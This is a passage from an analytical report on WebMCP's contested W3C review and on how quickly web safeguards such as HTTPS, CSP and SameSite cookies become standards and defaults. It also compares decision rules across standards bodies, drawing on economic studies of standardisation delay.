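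By late August, OpenAI supported WebMCP in the browser built into its ChatGPT desktop app, under the name "Site tools". Southern (2026) reported in *WebMCP Connects AI Agents To Actions Inside Websites* that Shopify and Cloudflare were also putting it into live products. The reviews were well behind this adoption. The minutes of 20 August, W3C's *WebML CG Teleconference* (2026), show that a draft threat model now existed but the privacy reviewers had not yet replied. The group did not decide to ask for accessibility and internationalisation reviews until that meeting.

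Browser makers also shipped Content Security Policy (CSP) before W3C had finished it. But CSP only restricts what a page can do, so an unfinished version mostly risked breaking sites or protecting them poorly. WebMCP gives agents a new way to act, and an unfinished version can expose people to attacks that a later one would prevent.

Early use hasn't stopped the design from changing, however. Nabors (2026), in *WebMCP connects the Web to AI Assistants and Agents*, lists several changes that would have broken early code. The group removed two functions in March, replaced another a few weeks later and then moved the whole interface to a different part of the browser's programming model.

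### Does the safety work belong somewhere else?

W3C TAG's *Incubation* (2026) contains notes from the TAG's discussions of WebMCP from June to October. On a 5 August call, Farolino told TAG members that many of the security objections were about agents in general rather than WebMCP in particular. For example, a careless agent can type someone's social security number into a pizza site using an ordinary HTML form. If W3C tied the solution to WebMCP and WebMCP then failed, agents would go on doing this.

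Farolino also argued that a web interface couldn't solve the problem. Nothing in a page's code can stop Claude from reading someone's email and then typing personal details into the wrong site. The agent's own software, or the browser around it, has to prevent that. According to Farolino, W3C's security group was sympathetic.

The evidence from browser agents supports this, since neither the attacks on ChatGPT Atlas nor defences such as Chrome's origin sets depend on WebMCP. Delaying the WebMCP standard until prompt injection is solved would leave people just as exposed to it in the meantime.

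Sarah Drasner, who joined the call in support of WebMCP, thought it could even make agents safer. Agents already scrape pages, and a site that offers tools can at least label the read-only ones. Idan Levin, whose company tests WebMCP, later added that an agent that looks for the right button must read more untrusted text than one that calls a named tool. This seems plausible for an honest site, but nobody on the call had measured it.

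Matthew Atkinson of the TAG accepted that agents carry these risks today, but wanted a new web feature to improve on the present situation. Adding WebMCP to browsers would officially bring agents into the web platform, and Atkinson argued that W3C would make matters worse if it did this before solving the security and privacy problems. In July, Atkinson had warned about standardising security holes "for which there is no known solution". Lola Odelola, another TAG member, said W3C shouldn't standardise a practice just because the industry had adopted it.

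The harm W3C's endorsement could do depends on whether companies wait for it. OpenAI and Shopify did not, but a finished standard might still persuade banks or public services to let agents act on their sites, where a failure could do more harm than at most shops.

Farolino's argument is weaker for problems that WebMCP itself creates or leaves open. One TAG reviewer found that the proposal glossed over authorisation, and others asked what happens if an agent reaches a login prompt partway through. Marcos Cáceres, a TAG member who also contributed to WebKit's response, said in September that the permissions layer was still missing and that WebMCP's developers knew it. Nick Doty, who chairs a W3C privacy group, had opened an issue about risks that the draft did nothing to mitigate. An agent's maker can't fully solve these problems alone, because the user's permissions must also be available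 to the site and the browser.

The TAG now seems to accept part of the distinction. It plans to publish its concerns about agentic browsing in a separate document, though it also considers them relevant to WebMCP.

### WebKit's alternative

WebKit's objection is mostly about design. Grigsby (2026), in *Improvements to Web for AI Should Benefit All Users*, quotes Mike Wyrzykowski of the Safari team, who argued that when a page's actions confuse an agent, the site should fix the gap in its markup using HTML and ARIA, a set of labels that describe a page's controls to screen readers. The fix would then also help people with disabilities. Wyrzykowski regards an agent as, in effect, assistive technology, which should operate a site as its user would.

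The Safari team also doubted that tools would be as reliable as promised, because an agent still has to interpret each tool's name and description, which are written in ordinary language. *Agents and closing gaps with existing semantics* reproduces Wyrzykowski's quotation from WebMCP's own specification, which states that there is "no guarantee" a tool does what it declares.

Farolino answered that many tasks, such as filtering what is on a page or adding an overlay in a picture editor, don't fit in a form. Yoav Weiss, who works on WebMCP at Shopify, gave the TAG a list of the tools that let agents search a Shopify shop's catalogue, manage orders, show a variant of a product and look up store policies. Agreeing on HTML for all of these could take years, and other kinds of site would need different tools. Levin went further, arguing that HTML rich enough to describe every action, with its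 inputs and side effects, would just be WebMCP in another form.

Farolino also cited Apple's own products as evidence. Siri's new AI features operate Mac apps only through App Intents, a programming interface much like WebMCP's, even though Mac apps already describe their controls well to assistive technology. If those descriptions were enough, Apple presumably wouldn't have needed App Intents.

Some TAG members would accept WebMCP's declarative half but want its developers to finish it before shipping the imperative half. Atkinson pointed out that W3C usually starts with the simpler, more predictable form of a feature. Farolino replied that in Chrome's trial, sites had registered imperative tools about 172 million times by 6 August, and declarative tools about 20,000 times.

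Those numbers show what developers prefer, but they probably exaggerate the gap because they count registrations, and a few large companies with busy sites could account for most of those. Cáceres wasn't impressed by the preference, remarking in September that JavaScript developers will use a JavaScript API if you give them one.

Cáceres also gave an example of what the imperative form can lose. A colleague's demonstration described the limits on a value in text for the model to read, although HTML's `min` and `max` attributes could have expressed them. If the seats field on a booking form has a maximum of 9, the browser can reject a request for 40, whereas a limit stated only in a tool's description depends on the model following it.

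Better HTML wouldn't stop prompt injection, though, or keep an agent from carrying data between sites. WebKit's approach has a smaller safety advantage, because people and agents would use the same controls and a person could see what the agent had to work with. Google emphasises in its Chrome for Developers introduction to WebMCP that tools run visibly on the page, but the user may see only the result and not the description that led the agent to choose the tool.

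Browser makers could address part of this by showing users the tools that a page offers to agents. Valkhof (2026), in *WebMCP is an exciting feature built for the wrong target*, likes the idea of WebMCP but objects that only agents get to use it. Valkhof's mock-up of Chrome has a "Page features" bar that shows users the page's tools. This would also let people notice a tool that shouldn't be there.

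### Users before authors

Drasner worried on the August call that the people who make websites had no voice in the discussion and were having agents imposed on them. Odelola replied that W3C puts users first. Its rule, which Grigsby quotes, ranks users above page authors, page authors above browser makers, and browser makers above the people who write specifications. Under this rule, if WebMCP helps page authors but puts users' security at risk, the risk outweighs the benefit. Gustafson sided with WebKit on similar grounds in *WebMCP Should Prioritize People over Agents*.

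WebMCP's supporters claim to follow the same principle. Drasner said that keeping users safe was their only interest, and that giving site developers more control would also benefit users. In *Why WebMCP matters*, Weiss (2026) argues that users can take over at any point when an agent works inside an open page. When an agent deals directly with a company's server, the user may have no page to take over.

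The rule gives no way to compare a faster agent with a safer one. WebMCP's supporters had a benchmark from Levin's company in which agents that worked from the page's structure used about 5 to 10 times as many tokens (the units of text that models process) and took 4 to 5 times as long as agents that used WebMCP. The TAG record has no comparable figures on how often an agent leaks data or buys the wrong thing with WebMCP and without it. Drasner had asked for a comparison of the two situations, and such a test would have given the reviewers better evidence about users' safety than the number of tools developers had registered.

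### After the October meetings

The TAG had not reached a final decision by late November. Its members disagreed from the start. Christian Liebel liked the proposal and thought its interface felt natural to developers. Cáceres called it naive and feared that it might affect the web's architecture more than any earlier proposal. Ehsan Toreini expected attackers to exploit WebMCP, but preferred steering it to blocking it because companies would go ahead anyway.

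Several members reasoned this way. Hadley Beeman thought agents would get such an interface whatever the TAG decided, but didn't want the TAG to drop its objections for that reason. Cáceres replied that WebMCP was only one possible version of the interface. The clearest drawback of the late review is probably that some reviewers no longer saw rejection as a practical choice. By the time the TAG discussed WebMCP in earnest, two browsers were testing it or about to.

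The TAG struggled to choose a label for its verdict. In October its members considered "satisfied with concerns", but Cáceres and another participant recalled earlier cases in which a group had noticed the "satisfied" and ignored the "concerns". Members also discussed "proceed with caution" and a new label for concerns that don't block a proposal.

On 26 October, Liebel posted an interim comment for the TAG, accepting that agents can be slow and error-prone on ordinary pages and that WebMCP addresses this. The comment also lists concerns that "ought to be addressed before WebMCP ships", although the TAG hadn't agreed on how much each one matters. The main fear is that a separate web for agents will develop, with functions that people and screen readers can't reach. Other concerns are more technical, such as tool descriptions written in a language that a small model can't read. The TAG also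 suggested renaming the proposal to something like "Tools", because the present name implies a closer link to MCP than exists.

Google had requested part of the delay. On 9 October, Farolino asked the TAG to wait for W3C's annual meeting and for an updated position from Mozilla. In mid-June, according to *WebMCP's open question, answered from accessibility* (2026), a Mozilla reviewer had proposed marking WebMCP "neutral" and looking at it again later. By August, Farolino reported that Mozilla agreed HTML alone wouldn't be enough and supported the imperative API in particular, with changes. This was Google's account of Mozilla's view, and Mozilla's own updated position was still pending in October.

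The other open question was which W3C group should turn WebMCP into a standard. In June its developers proposed moving it from the Community Group to the related Web Machine Learning Working Group, which can publish standards. The minutes describe a draft change to that group's charter (W3C, 2026). Mozilla's representative thought it made sense to advance, while Apple's early feedback was to move the work to a different group (log of the same meeting, W3C, 2026). Cáceres wanted a workshop on agents first, then a new group.

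The plan for an Agentic Web Working Group, which de Vries reported from the October meetings, partly addresses that, but the group still needs an approved charter. Apple's objection to the venue may therefore have had more effect so far than its objection to the design. In November, WebMCP was still a Community Group draft, with trials running in Chrome and Edge.

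## How long does a safeguard take to become a standard and then a default?

A web safeguard can become a default about 15 months after its developers announce the change, or more than 30 years after its invention. The formal standard often comes after most people already use the safeguard, and sometimes it never comes. WebMCP is therefore not unusual in spreading as an unfinished draft, though it has spread quickly.

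### Five dates

The history of a safeguard can include five dates:

- first proposal, when someone publicly describes the mechanism
- first release, when people outside the company that built it can use it
- formal standard, when W3C publishes a Recommendation or the IETF approves a document on its standards track
- majority use, when more than half of the relevant sites or page loads have it
- on by default, when a widely used product applies it unless someone turns it off.

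The years in parentheses count from the first proposal.

| Safeguard | First proposal | First release | Formal standard | Majority use | On by default |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Content Security Policy | 2007 | March 2011 (4 years) | December 2016 (9 years) | Not reached: about 22% of sites in 2025 | Not reached |
| HTTPS | 1994 | Mid-1990s | June 2022 (28 years) | Page loads: early 2017 (23 years). Top million sites: by March 2020 (26 years) | October 2026, in Chrome (32 years) |
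| Permissions Policy | By April 2019 | By September 2020 | Not reached: Working Draft in June 2026 | No figure | Varies by feature |

The IETF published a description of HTTPS in May 2000, labeled "Informational". HTTPS joined the standards track only in 2022, as part of *HTTP Semantics*, the IETF's main specification of HTTP. By then, most page loads had used HTTPS for about five years.

CSP became a formal standard much sooner, but most sites still don't use it. Browser makers had the agreement they needed even before CSP was formally a standard. According to W3C's publication history, CSP Level 2 took 26 months to go from first draft to Candidate Recommendation, which requires the working group's consensus. It took another 22 months to become a Recommendation, and by then three browsers already supported it.

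These intervals depend on somewhat arbitrary choices of start and release dates. Some histories trace CSP to 2004, which would add three years to each of its figures. The Permissions Policy row starts with W3C's first public draft and ends when Google announced a replacement for a header that Chrome already supported. The actual start and release were probably both earlier, so the gap between the listed dates means little.

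Permission prompts don't fit the table well, because a browser can show them without any work by the site. A safeguard introduced with a new feature can be on by default from the first day, since no existing site relies on the feature working without it. Safeguards for older features, such as cookies, have to change how existing sites work.

### robots.txt: 28 years without a formal standard

A site can publish a file called `robots.txt` to tell crawlers, the programs that collect pages for search engines, which parts to avoid. A travel site might use this one:

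```
User-agent: *
Disallow: /bookings/
```

The file is a request for all crawlers to stay out of the bookings folder. It can't stop a crawler that ignores the request, so it resembles a tool annotation more than a sandbox.

*Robots Exclusion Protocol* (Koster, 2022) dates the method to 1994, and the IETF (2022) records its publication as a Proposed Standard on 9 September 2022, about 28 years later. A pre-publication copy (Koster, Illyes and colleagues, 2022) gives the starting year as 1996, which would shorten the interval to 26 years.

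The RFC added a precise grammar and instructions for handling errors and caching. Before that, if a crawler got a server error when requesting the file, its developer had no official rule on whether to treat the site as open or closed. Crawlers and site owners evidently managed without one, but the late standard gave developers a common answer to questions that the original method had not settled.

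### SameSite cookies: a default in 15 months

Suppose the employee is signed in to the airline's site and opens a malicious page in another tab. The page submits a hidden form to the airline's server. The browser attaches the airline's cookie, so the request looks like the employee's own. Security engineers call this cross-site request forgery.

A site can prevent many of these attacks by adding a `SameSite` setting to its cookie:

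```
Set-Cookie: session=abc123; SameSite=Lax; Secure
```

With `Lax`, the browser sends the cookie when the employee follows a link to the airline, but not when another site submits a form. At first, sites had to choose `Lax` themselves. Google then decided that Chrome would treat any cookie without a `SameSite` setting as `Lax`. Sites that needed their cookies to work inside other sites had to mark them `SameSite=None; Secure`.

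Chromium Blog's *SameSite Cookie Changes in February 2020* (2020) dates the announcement to May 2019. The later steps come from Google's *SameSite Updates*:

- In October 2019, Google turned the new default on for half the users of Chrome's early test versions.
- In the week of 17 February 2020, it began a limited rollout in the ordinary version.
- On 3 April, it withdrew the change.
- On 14 July, it started again.
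- On 11 August, it raised the target to all users of recent versions.

Google publicly attributed the withdrawal to the COVID-19 pandemic. On a mailing list archived by IETF (2020), Google engineer Mike West wrote that the change had reached about half of Chrome's ordinary users and caused "unexpected breakage at a particularly bad time". Both explanations can be true, because a broken login page matters more when people can't visit a shop or office instead.

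Google also had to weaken the default to avoid breaking some logins. The last step of signing in is sometimes a form that one site submits to another, and the receiving site needs a cookie it set moments earlier. Chrome therefore still sends cookies that have no `SameSite` setting with these forms if the cookies are no more than two minutes old. Google described the exception as temporary in November 2019. Six years later, IETF's *Cookies* (2025) still included a mode for this purpose, also as a temporary measure, and described `Lax` as "difficult to apply as the default behavior".

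The formal standard took much longer than the rollout. *HTTP State Management Mechanism* (Barth and West, 2016) began the revision of the cookie specification that now covers `SameSite`. The IETF's steering group approved the revision on 2 December 2025, nine years after that draft and more than five years after Chrome changed its default. The approval notice, *Protocol Action* (IESG, 2025), reports broad agreement and no particular controversy, so a long delay doesn't always mean people disagreed. By July 2026, van Kesteren and Hofmann were already drafting a successor, *Cookies* (2026).

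A default in one browser may not become the default in others. In May 2020, Mozilla had the same change turned on for all users of Firefox's nightly test version, but its tracking entry, baku's *Enable sameSite=lax by default*, still had no release date in April 2024.

### A deadline of 102 days

Browser makers can set much shorter deadlines when they consider a threat urgent. On 3 December 2026, Google's *Keeping HTTPS Connections Safe in Chrome* (2026) announced that Chrome would stop trusting certificate authorities' ECDSA P-256 keys, one of the types they use to sign certificates, after 15 March 2027, 102 days later. Visitors to a site whose certificate depends on such a key will then see a full-page warning.

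Google cites "increased urgency" as its reason for speeding up the move to cryptography that quantum computers can't break. By comparison, Thompson and colleagues gave sites a year's notice of Chrome's HTTP warning.

Google can attempt this because Chrome decides which certificate authorities it trusts, and they are few enough to contact individually. Automation should also help, because a site that automatically gets a new certificate every 90 days will normally replace its old one before the deadline, if its authority has switched keys. Sites that install certificates by hand have more to do, and some will probably miss the deadline.

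Google's longer-term plan is also ahead of the formal standards process. Google expects certificate authorities to offer a new kind of certificate, the Merkle Tree Certificate, very early in 2027, but the specification is still an IETF Internet-Draft.

### What makes a protocol succeed?

*What Makes for a Successful Protocol?* (Thaler and Aboba, 2008) compares eight case studies of internet technologies and concludes that two things matter most at the start. The technology has to meet a real need, ideally with a clear net benefit for every organisation that must change something. It also has to work incrementally, so that early adopters benefit before everyone else joins.

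Multicast between networks was meant to let a sender transmit one stream, such as a video, to many receivers without sending a separate copy to each. It failed on both counts because every router along the way had to support it, and network operators would have paid for much of the work while most of the benefit went to applications.

By contrast, WEP, an early encryption system for Wi-Fi, was poorly designed but spread widely because each network's owner could turn it on independently and had no alternative. Thaler and Aboba found that technical quality and security had little effect on initial success. Attackers often ignore technology that few people use, so its weaknesses may not matter until it is popular.

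They also found that many successful protocols began outside standards bodies and became formal standards only later. Free, open code mattered more at first than an open process for maintaining the specification. They suggest waiting 5 to 10 years before deciding that an average protocol has failed.

These conclusions come from a few examples chosen to illustrate them, though including failures such as multicast makes them more convincing. They also concern protocols in general rather than safeguards in particular. WEP counts as a success because people used it, but a popular safeguard can still protect people badly, as many CSP policies do.

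### Testing four predictors

The web cases provide a rough test of four possible predictors of speed: who bears the burden, how many parties must act, whether an early adopter benefits even if no one else adopts the safeguard, and whether failure is visible.

The evidence is strongest that effort and expense slow adoption, because these varied within single safeguards. CSP's one-line framing rule did much better than its laborious script rules, although both use the same header. HTTPS spread much faster once certificates were free and automatic, though browser makers also pressured sites to adopt it.

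The number of parties involved also matters, but a small number doesn't guarantee speed. A CSP involves only one site and its visitors' browsers, yet most sites still don't have one. Chrome's cookie default changed quickly because one company could change it for everyone. But many sites then had to adapt, and those that hadn't were part of the reason for the rollback. Having few parties probably helps most when they can do the work for many others, as hosting companies did with certificates.

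HTTPS and CSP both benefit early adopters, so that benefit can't explain why HTTPS spread further. A site that adopts either one protects its own visitors even if no other site does. Such a benefit may still be necessary for success, as multicast's failure suggests. The table can't be used to test this, because it contains only safeguards that survived long enough to become well known. It leaves out any that failed because early adopters gained nothing.

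People remove safeguards that visibly break something, as Airbnb did with its first CSP policy and Google did with the cookie default. They have a reason to add a safeguard when its absence is visible, as it is with Chrome's HTTP warning.

Users often notice the drawbacks of agent safeguards more easily than the benefits, which can slow adoption. A sandbox that blocks a legitimate command annoys the user at once, but the user may not notice when an agent leaks a passport number. A platform could make missing safeguards more visible, for example by warning people before they connect an agent that has no sandbox.

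These patterns come from only a few cases and may not hold in others. The predictors also overlap. Free certificates, for instance, reduced both the cost to site owners and the number of people who had to do the work.

### MCP and WebMCP on the same scale

| Date | MCP's authorisation system | WebMCP |
|---|---|---|
| First proposal | By March 2025 | August 2025 |
| First release | March 2025 | Preview in February 2026; trial with real users in June 2026 |
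| Formal standard | Not reached | Not reached: Community Group draft in November 2026 |
| Majority use | No figure | No figure |
| On by default | Not reached: still optional | Not reached: trials in two browsers |

MCP itself has spread much faster than HTTPS or CSP did. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports that monthly downloads of MCP's software kits quadrupled in the first seven months of the year. Anthropic, which created MCP, calls it the "industry standard" for connecting agents to applications. That may fairly describe how widely developers use it, but no formal standards body has approved it.

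Thaler and Aboba's factors explain much of this growth. The code is free, a company can add a server without waiting for its competitors, and the server can work with existing agents straight away. But the downloads measure how quickly agents are gaining abilities, not how many servers require authorisation or how many clients ask the user before making a purchase.

MCP's safeguards also vary in how well they fit the predictors. Authorisation protects the airline that sets it up, whereas annotations mostly benefit the agent's user, even though the airline does the labelling.

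WebMCP's trials will show whether sites have enough reason to supply accurate labels. Its origin limits can become a default more easily, because they arrived with the feature and the browser applies them. If WebMCP becomes a default, the limits can become one at the same time, without changes to millions of sites.

Neither MCP nor WebMCP is old enough to judge by Thaler and Aboba's five-year criterion. MCP will turn five in November 2029, and WebMCP in August 2030 if the count starts with its first explainer. Waiting that long to assess their security would be unwise, because attackers will have more reason to target both as more people use them.

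A formal standard could take longer still. If W3C's proposed Agentic Web Working Group published its first draft in mid-2027 and moved at the pace of CSP Level 2, it would finish in roughly mid-2031. Browsers could enforce the rules well before then, as they did with CSP, so people could be safer before the standard is final.

Agents may change too quickly for older timelines to be a good guide. MCP had five specification releases in 20 months, and Delimarsky and Soria Parra now plan two a year, partly so that developers know when the text will stop changing. Products can change even faster. Claude Code's auto mode became the default on some plans about five months after Anthropic described it. A safeguard designed around approval prompts in early 2026 would already need to work with a classifier that handles most of them.

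## Which ways of making standards reach agreement sooner, and at what cost?

Google gave certificate authorities 102 days to stop relying on one type of key, whereas the IETF took nine years to revise its cookie specification. One reason for the difference is that Google could decide alone. Involving more people usually slows a decision, but it gives them a chance to find mistakes and object.

### How five bodies decide

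The IETF makes decisions by rough consensus, which *On Consensus and Humming in the IETF* (Resnick, 2014) explains. It doesn't vote because it has no formal members, so nobody could say who was entitled to vote. Suppose a working group is choosing how an agent should prove that its user approved a purchase, and one engineer objects that the proposed format would reveal the user's travel history. The group must either fix the problem or explain why it isn't serious enough to stop the work. The chair then judges whether the group has answered the objection.

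A large majority isn't enough if the group hasn't addressed an objection. Once it has, one person who still disagrees can't block the decision, though that person can appeal. Resnick advises chairs to ask "Can anyone not live with choice A?" rather than whether everyone likes it, because almost any design will have critics.

W3C also seeks consensus, and it requires evidence that people can implement a standard before its member organisations review the document. In August 2025, it removed a separate stage near the end of the process, so members now review a Candidate Recommendation directly (W3C, 2025). Working groups had complained that the stage caused delay without adding useful review, according to PPC Land's *W3C streamlines web standards process with major document updates*. The change reduces paperwork, but developers still need time to build and test a feature.

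Someone who disagrees with a W3C decision can file a Formal Objection. W3C staff have 90 days to investigate and look for a compromise. If they don't find one, a council decides whether to overrule the objection or cancel the decision. The council can suggest a different design but can't impose one.

Members can also object to a new group's charter, so a dispute could delay the proposed Agentic Web Working Group before it writes anything. W3C's 2025 rules added a formal discussion period for draft charters, partly to settle such disputes earlier.

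At the WHATWG, browser makers have much more control. Only a standard's editor may change its text, and van Kesteren (2017), one of the editors, told a contributor that a change needed interest from at least two implementers. Under WHATWG's *Steering Group Agreement* (2017), Apple, Google, Microsoft and Mozilla make the final decisions. They usually proceed if nobody objects strongly, but any of them can call for a vote, which requires a two-thirds majority, or three of the four members. Only companies that develop a major browser engine and distribute it widely can join, so a company that makes agents without an engine can contribute ideas but can't vote.

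The CA/Browser Forum sets rules for the certificates behind HTTPS. Certificate issuers and browser makers vote separately. A proposal needs support from at least two-thirds of the issuers that vote and more than half of the browser makers that vote, so either side can block it.

MCP's maintainers decide on written proposals. When Anthropic gave the project to the Agentic AI Foundation in December 2025, anyone could write a proposal, but a maintainer had to sponsor it. A small group of core maintainers then decided, and the lead maintainers could veto their decision. The foundation's board managed money and membership, while the maintainers kept control of the protocol.

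| Body | What helps it decide sooner | What it gives up |
|---|---|---|
| IETF | An objector can't block a group that has answered the objection | Certainty, because much depends on the chair's judgement |
| W3C | A council can end a dispute | Some speed, in return for wide review and evidence from implementations |
| WHATWG | Few companies have the final say, and they build the browsers | A vote for site owners, users and most agent developers |
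| CA/Browser Forum | A vote settles the matter | A vote for the sites that have to install the certificates |
| MCP | A small group decides | Formal review by a body independent of the project |

### How commercial conflict slowed the IETF

Consensus becomes harder to reach when companies have money at stake. Simcoe measured how much harder it became at the IETF as the internet became commercial (*Standard Setting Committees*, 2010; later version in the *American Economic Review*, 2012). Private-sector participation in the IETF rose from about 50% in 1993 to over 80% in 2001.

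Simcoe followed 2,601 Internet-Drafts that working groups received between 1993 and 2003. Simcoe's "suit-to-beard" ratio was the share of organisations on each group's mailing list with .com or .net addresses. A high ratio was a sign that the group's work mattered to companies' products.

A commercial group might also be slow because its technology is difficult. To separate the two causes, Simcoe compared proposed standards with the informational and experimental documents that the same groups publish. Both kinds go through the same steps, but companies have little reason to fight over the informational and experimental ones, which the IETF doesn't endorse. If difficult technology were the whole explanation, both kinds should have slowed down together.

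Proposed standards took an average of 774 days, compared with 595 for the other documents. Each additional percentage point of private-sector participation in a group widened that gap by 7.8 days. Participation rose by about 30 points over the period, which implies a delay of 234 days, or nearly eight months.

The exact size of the effect is uncertain, as Simcoe's other methods gave between 4.2 and 12.3 days per point. Authors sometimes turn a controversial standard into an informational document, which hides some of the conflict. To allow for this, Simcoe counted words such as MUST and SHOULD in the first draft, a sign that the authors had intended to write a standard. This method gave the highest estimate.

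Conflict caused the most delay in the areas closest to applications, where companies were inventing new products, and little in the older protocols underneath. Agent protocols also involve new and competing products, so similar delays seem likely. However, the data are more than 20 years old and come from one organisation. Commercial conflict also doesn't explain every delay, since the cookie revision was delayed even though it was uncontroversial.

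In the main analysis, proposals from academic and non-profit authors took about five months longer to reach agreement than other documents. Simcoe suggests these authors had less to offer companies in return for the companies' support. The result was weaker when Simcoe compared proposals within the same working group.

### When is it better to toss a coin?

Holding out for a preferred design can be beneficial because the company with the best design has the most reason to hold out. *Choosing the Rules for Consensus Standardization* (Farrell and Simcoe, 2009; published in the *RAND Journal of Economics* in 2012) presents a model of this.

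Two companies each propose a design. Each knows how good its own design is, but not the other's. They can't combine the designs or pay each other to agree, so they argue until one gives up. Both would prefer either design to having no standard, and both benefit more from a better design. But the company whose design is chosen benefits more than the other, perhaps because its products already use it.

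A company with a weak design gives up sooner than one with a strong design, because the other design is probably better and it loses by waiting. The better design therefore wins, but everyone has to wait for it, and the wait is longer when winning is worth more.

Suppose the worst possible design is worth 1 and the average design is worth 2. Most designs are fairly weak, but a few are excellent. (In the mathematics, the chance that a design is worth more than *x* is 1/*x*².) Tossing a coin on the first day gives an average value of 2. Farrell and Simcoe's formulas give the following values for holding out, after subtracting the cost of delay:

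| Winner's benefit compared with loser's | Coin toss | Holding out |
|---|---|---|
| The same | 2.00 | 2.67 |
| 1.5 times as much | 2.00 | 2.29 |
| Twice as much | 2.00 | 2.00 |
| 3 times as much | 2.00 | 1.60 |

When neither company has much at stake, arguing over the designs helps them choose the better one with little delay. If the winner gets three times as much as the loser, the harm from the delay outweighs the benefit of the better design.

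Companies can argue longest over the choices that matter least, which the averages don't show. In the second row, if one design is worth 6 and the other 1.2, the company with the weaker design soon gives up. The result is worth about 5.5 after the delay, compared with an average of 3.6 for a coin toss. If the designs are worth 6 and 5, both companies hold out for a long time, and the result is worth only about 2.7, compared with an average of 5.5 for a coin toss.

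Farrell and Simcoe found that a neutral tie-breaker can often do better than either method. The companies argue for a while, which gives the sponsor of a weak design time to withdraw. The tie-breaker then picks one of the remaining designs, without needing to know which is better. The more the companies have at stake, the sooner the tie-breaker should step in.

W3C's council can reject a group's decision but can't choose a rival design, so it doesn't quite fill this role. An IETF chair comes closer, but has to justify a decision on technical grounds. A coin toss might also leave the losing company unwilling to adopt the standard.

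Another way to reduce delay is to make winning less valuable. Rules on patent licensing can do this, and W3C's royalty-free rule already removes one way to profit from a standard. Starting before companies have products to defend can also help, but they will then know less about which design is best. Farrell and Simcoe give the example of the internet's original 32-bit addresses, whose designers didn't foresee how many addresses people would need. More frequent meetings probably wouldn't help much if the companies are mainly waiting for each other to give up.

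The model includes only the benefits to the two companies. With an agent safeguard, many of the benefits go to users who aren't at the meeting, so a design that suits both companies could still leave a traveller's passport number poorly protected.

### Do Not Track

Browser makers quickly agreed on how to send a Do Not Track request, but W3C's group never got websites to agree on how to respond. If a user turned the setting on, the browser added a short header to its requests:

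```
DNT: 1
```

Firefox introduced the Do Not Track setting in 2011, and other browsers followed. The W3C formed a working group to standardize it that September, with browser makers, advertisers and privacy advocates among its members. They disagreed about whether a site that received a Do Not Track request had to stop collecting data or only stop using it to choose advertisements.

In 2012, Microsoft announced that Internet Explorer 10 would send the Do Not Track request by default. Advertisers objected that the header would no longer express a user's choice. The main alliance of US advertising groups left the W3C working group in 2013. W3C closed the group in January 2019 without publishing a Recommendation, because too few companies had adopted its work.

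Farrell and Simcoe's model assumes that everyone prefers some standard to none. Many advertisers preferred none, since they could keep collecting data as long as the group argued. A tie-breaker wouldn't have solved this, because a website could ignore the result.

A later signal, Global Privacy Control, works in much the same way, but California law requires many businesses to treat it as a request not to sell or share a person's data. It could therefore take effect without every advertiser's agreement. In 2022, the retailer Sephora agreed to pay $1.2 million to settle the state's claims that it had, among other things, ignored the signal.

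Files that list what agents may do on a website could fail as Do Not Track did, unless software or a law makes agents obey them.

### A vote to shorten certificates

A shorter certificate lifetime limits how long an attacker can use a stolen key, but sites have to replace their certificates more often. In 2019, Google proposed that the CA/Browser Forum cut the maximum from 825 days to 398. All the browser makers that voted were in favour, but only about a third of the issuers were, so the proposal failed.

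The defeat delayed the change by only about a year. In February 2020, Apple announced that starting that September, Safari would reject new certificates valid for more than 398 days. An issuer can't sell many certificates that don't work on iPhones, so the industry had to comply.

Apple proposed a much larger cut in October 2024. Its first draft would have reduced the maximum to 45 days in 2027. After months of discussion, the Forum approved a slower schedule in April 2025:

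- 200 days from 15 March 2026
- 100 days from 15 March 2027
- 47 days from 15 March 2029.

This time 25 issuers voted in favour, none voted against and five abstained. All four browser makers that voted supported the change. Agreement took about six months, and site owners got nearly four years to prepare for the shortest lifetime.

The issuers probably liked the idea less than the unanimous vote suggests. They had learned in 2020 that a browser maker could act without them, and a vote at least let them negotiate the dates. Automatic renewal had also become much more common, so the change was less of a burden than it would have been in 2019. Although the issuers had little power to refuse, the discussion seems to have been useful because it gave hospitals, banks and others with old equipment two more years.

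### Chrome's notice of 3 December

Google announced, without a CA/Browser Forum vote, that Chrome would stop trusting certificate authorities' P-256 keys. *Four Paths to Compatibility* (Farrell and Simcoe, 2011) lists following a leader as one alternative to negotiating in a committee. Here the leader is Chrome, and most sites can't do without its users.

Google says it contacted every certificate authority that uses the affected keys. It advises site owners to check all the certificates in their chain and get any replacements through their authority or hosting company. Google also encourages them to replace their own servers' P-256 keys, although the 15 March 2027 deadline covers only the authorities' keys. The Forum's 100-day limit begins the same day.

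A committee would have struggled to act this quickly, and attackers could exploit the delay if they found a way to break these keys. But 102 days leaves little time to discover problems, such as a payment terminal or medical device that accepts only certificates from the old authority. Companies that own such devices have no vote and no formal way to appeal.

Google's power also depends on its market share. A small browser that rejected the same certificates would mostly lose users, because people would blame the browser when sites stopped working.

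A company can more easily justify acting alone to fix an urgent flaw than to choose between competing designs. Without waiting for W3C to agree on a response, Chrome could reasonably block a method that attackers use to hijack agents. But competitors would have good reason to object if Google used the same power to make every site adopt Google's tool format.

### Origin trials as evidence

Origin trials let browser makers learn from real use before they commit to a design. Earlier, they often released unfinished features to everyone with a prefix on their names, such as `-webkit-` in CSS. Developers used the prefixed names on live sites, and Mozilla eventually had to support some of them in Firefox so those sites would work.

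Chrome designs its trials to prevent this kind of dependence. A site has to register to use a feature, and its permission expires. Chrome also normally turns the feature off if more than 0.5% of all page loads use it. Developers therefore know the feature might change or disappear.

These limits help, but a company that has built part of its business on a trial feature will still want to keep it. The company running the trial can then use that demand to argue for standardising the feature, as WebMCP's supporters did when they cited 172 million tool registrations.

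Trials are better at showing whether developers want a feature than whether it is safe. A trial of an agent feature would be more useful to reviewers if its sponsor agreed in advance to measure wrong purchases and data leaks, and to end the trial if they were too common.

### Europe's late standards

The European Union tried to use a legal deadline to get standards agreed sooner. Its AI Act sets duties for high-risk systems, such as those that screen job applicants, and leaves much of the technical detail to European standards. A company that follows these standards can presume it meets the legal requirements they cover. Without them, it has to work out for itself what a duty such as "appropriate" accuracy means.

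In May 2023, the European Commission asked two standards bodies, CEN and CENELEC, to write the standards by April 2025. They missed the deadline. In October 2025, they agreed to exceptional measures to speed up the work, including letting a draft skip its final vote if it had passed an earlier one.

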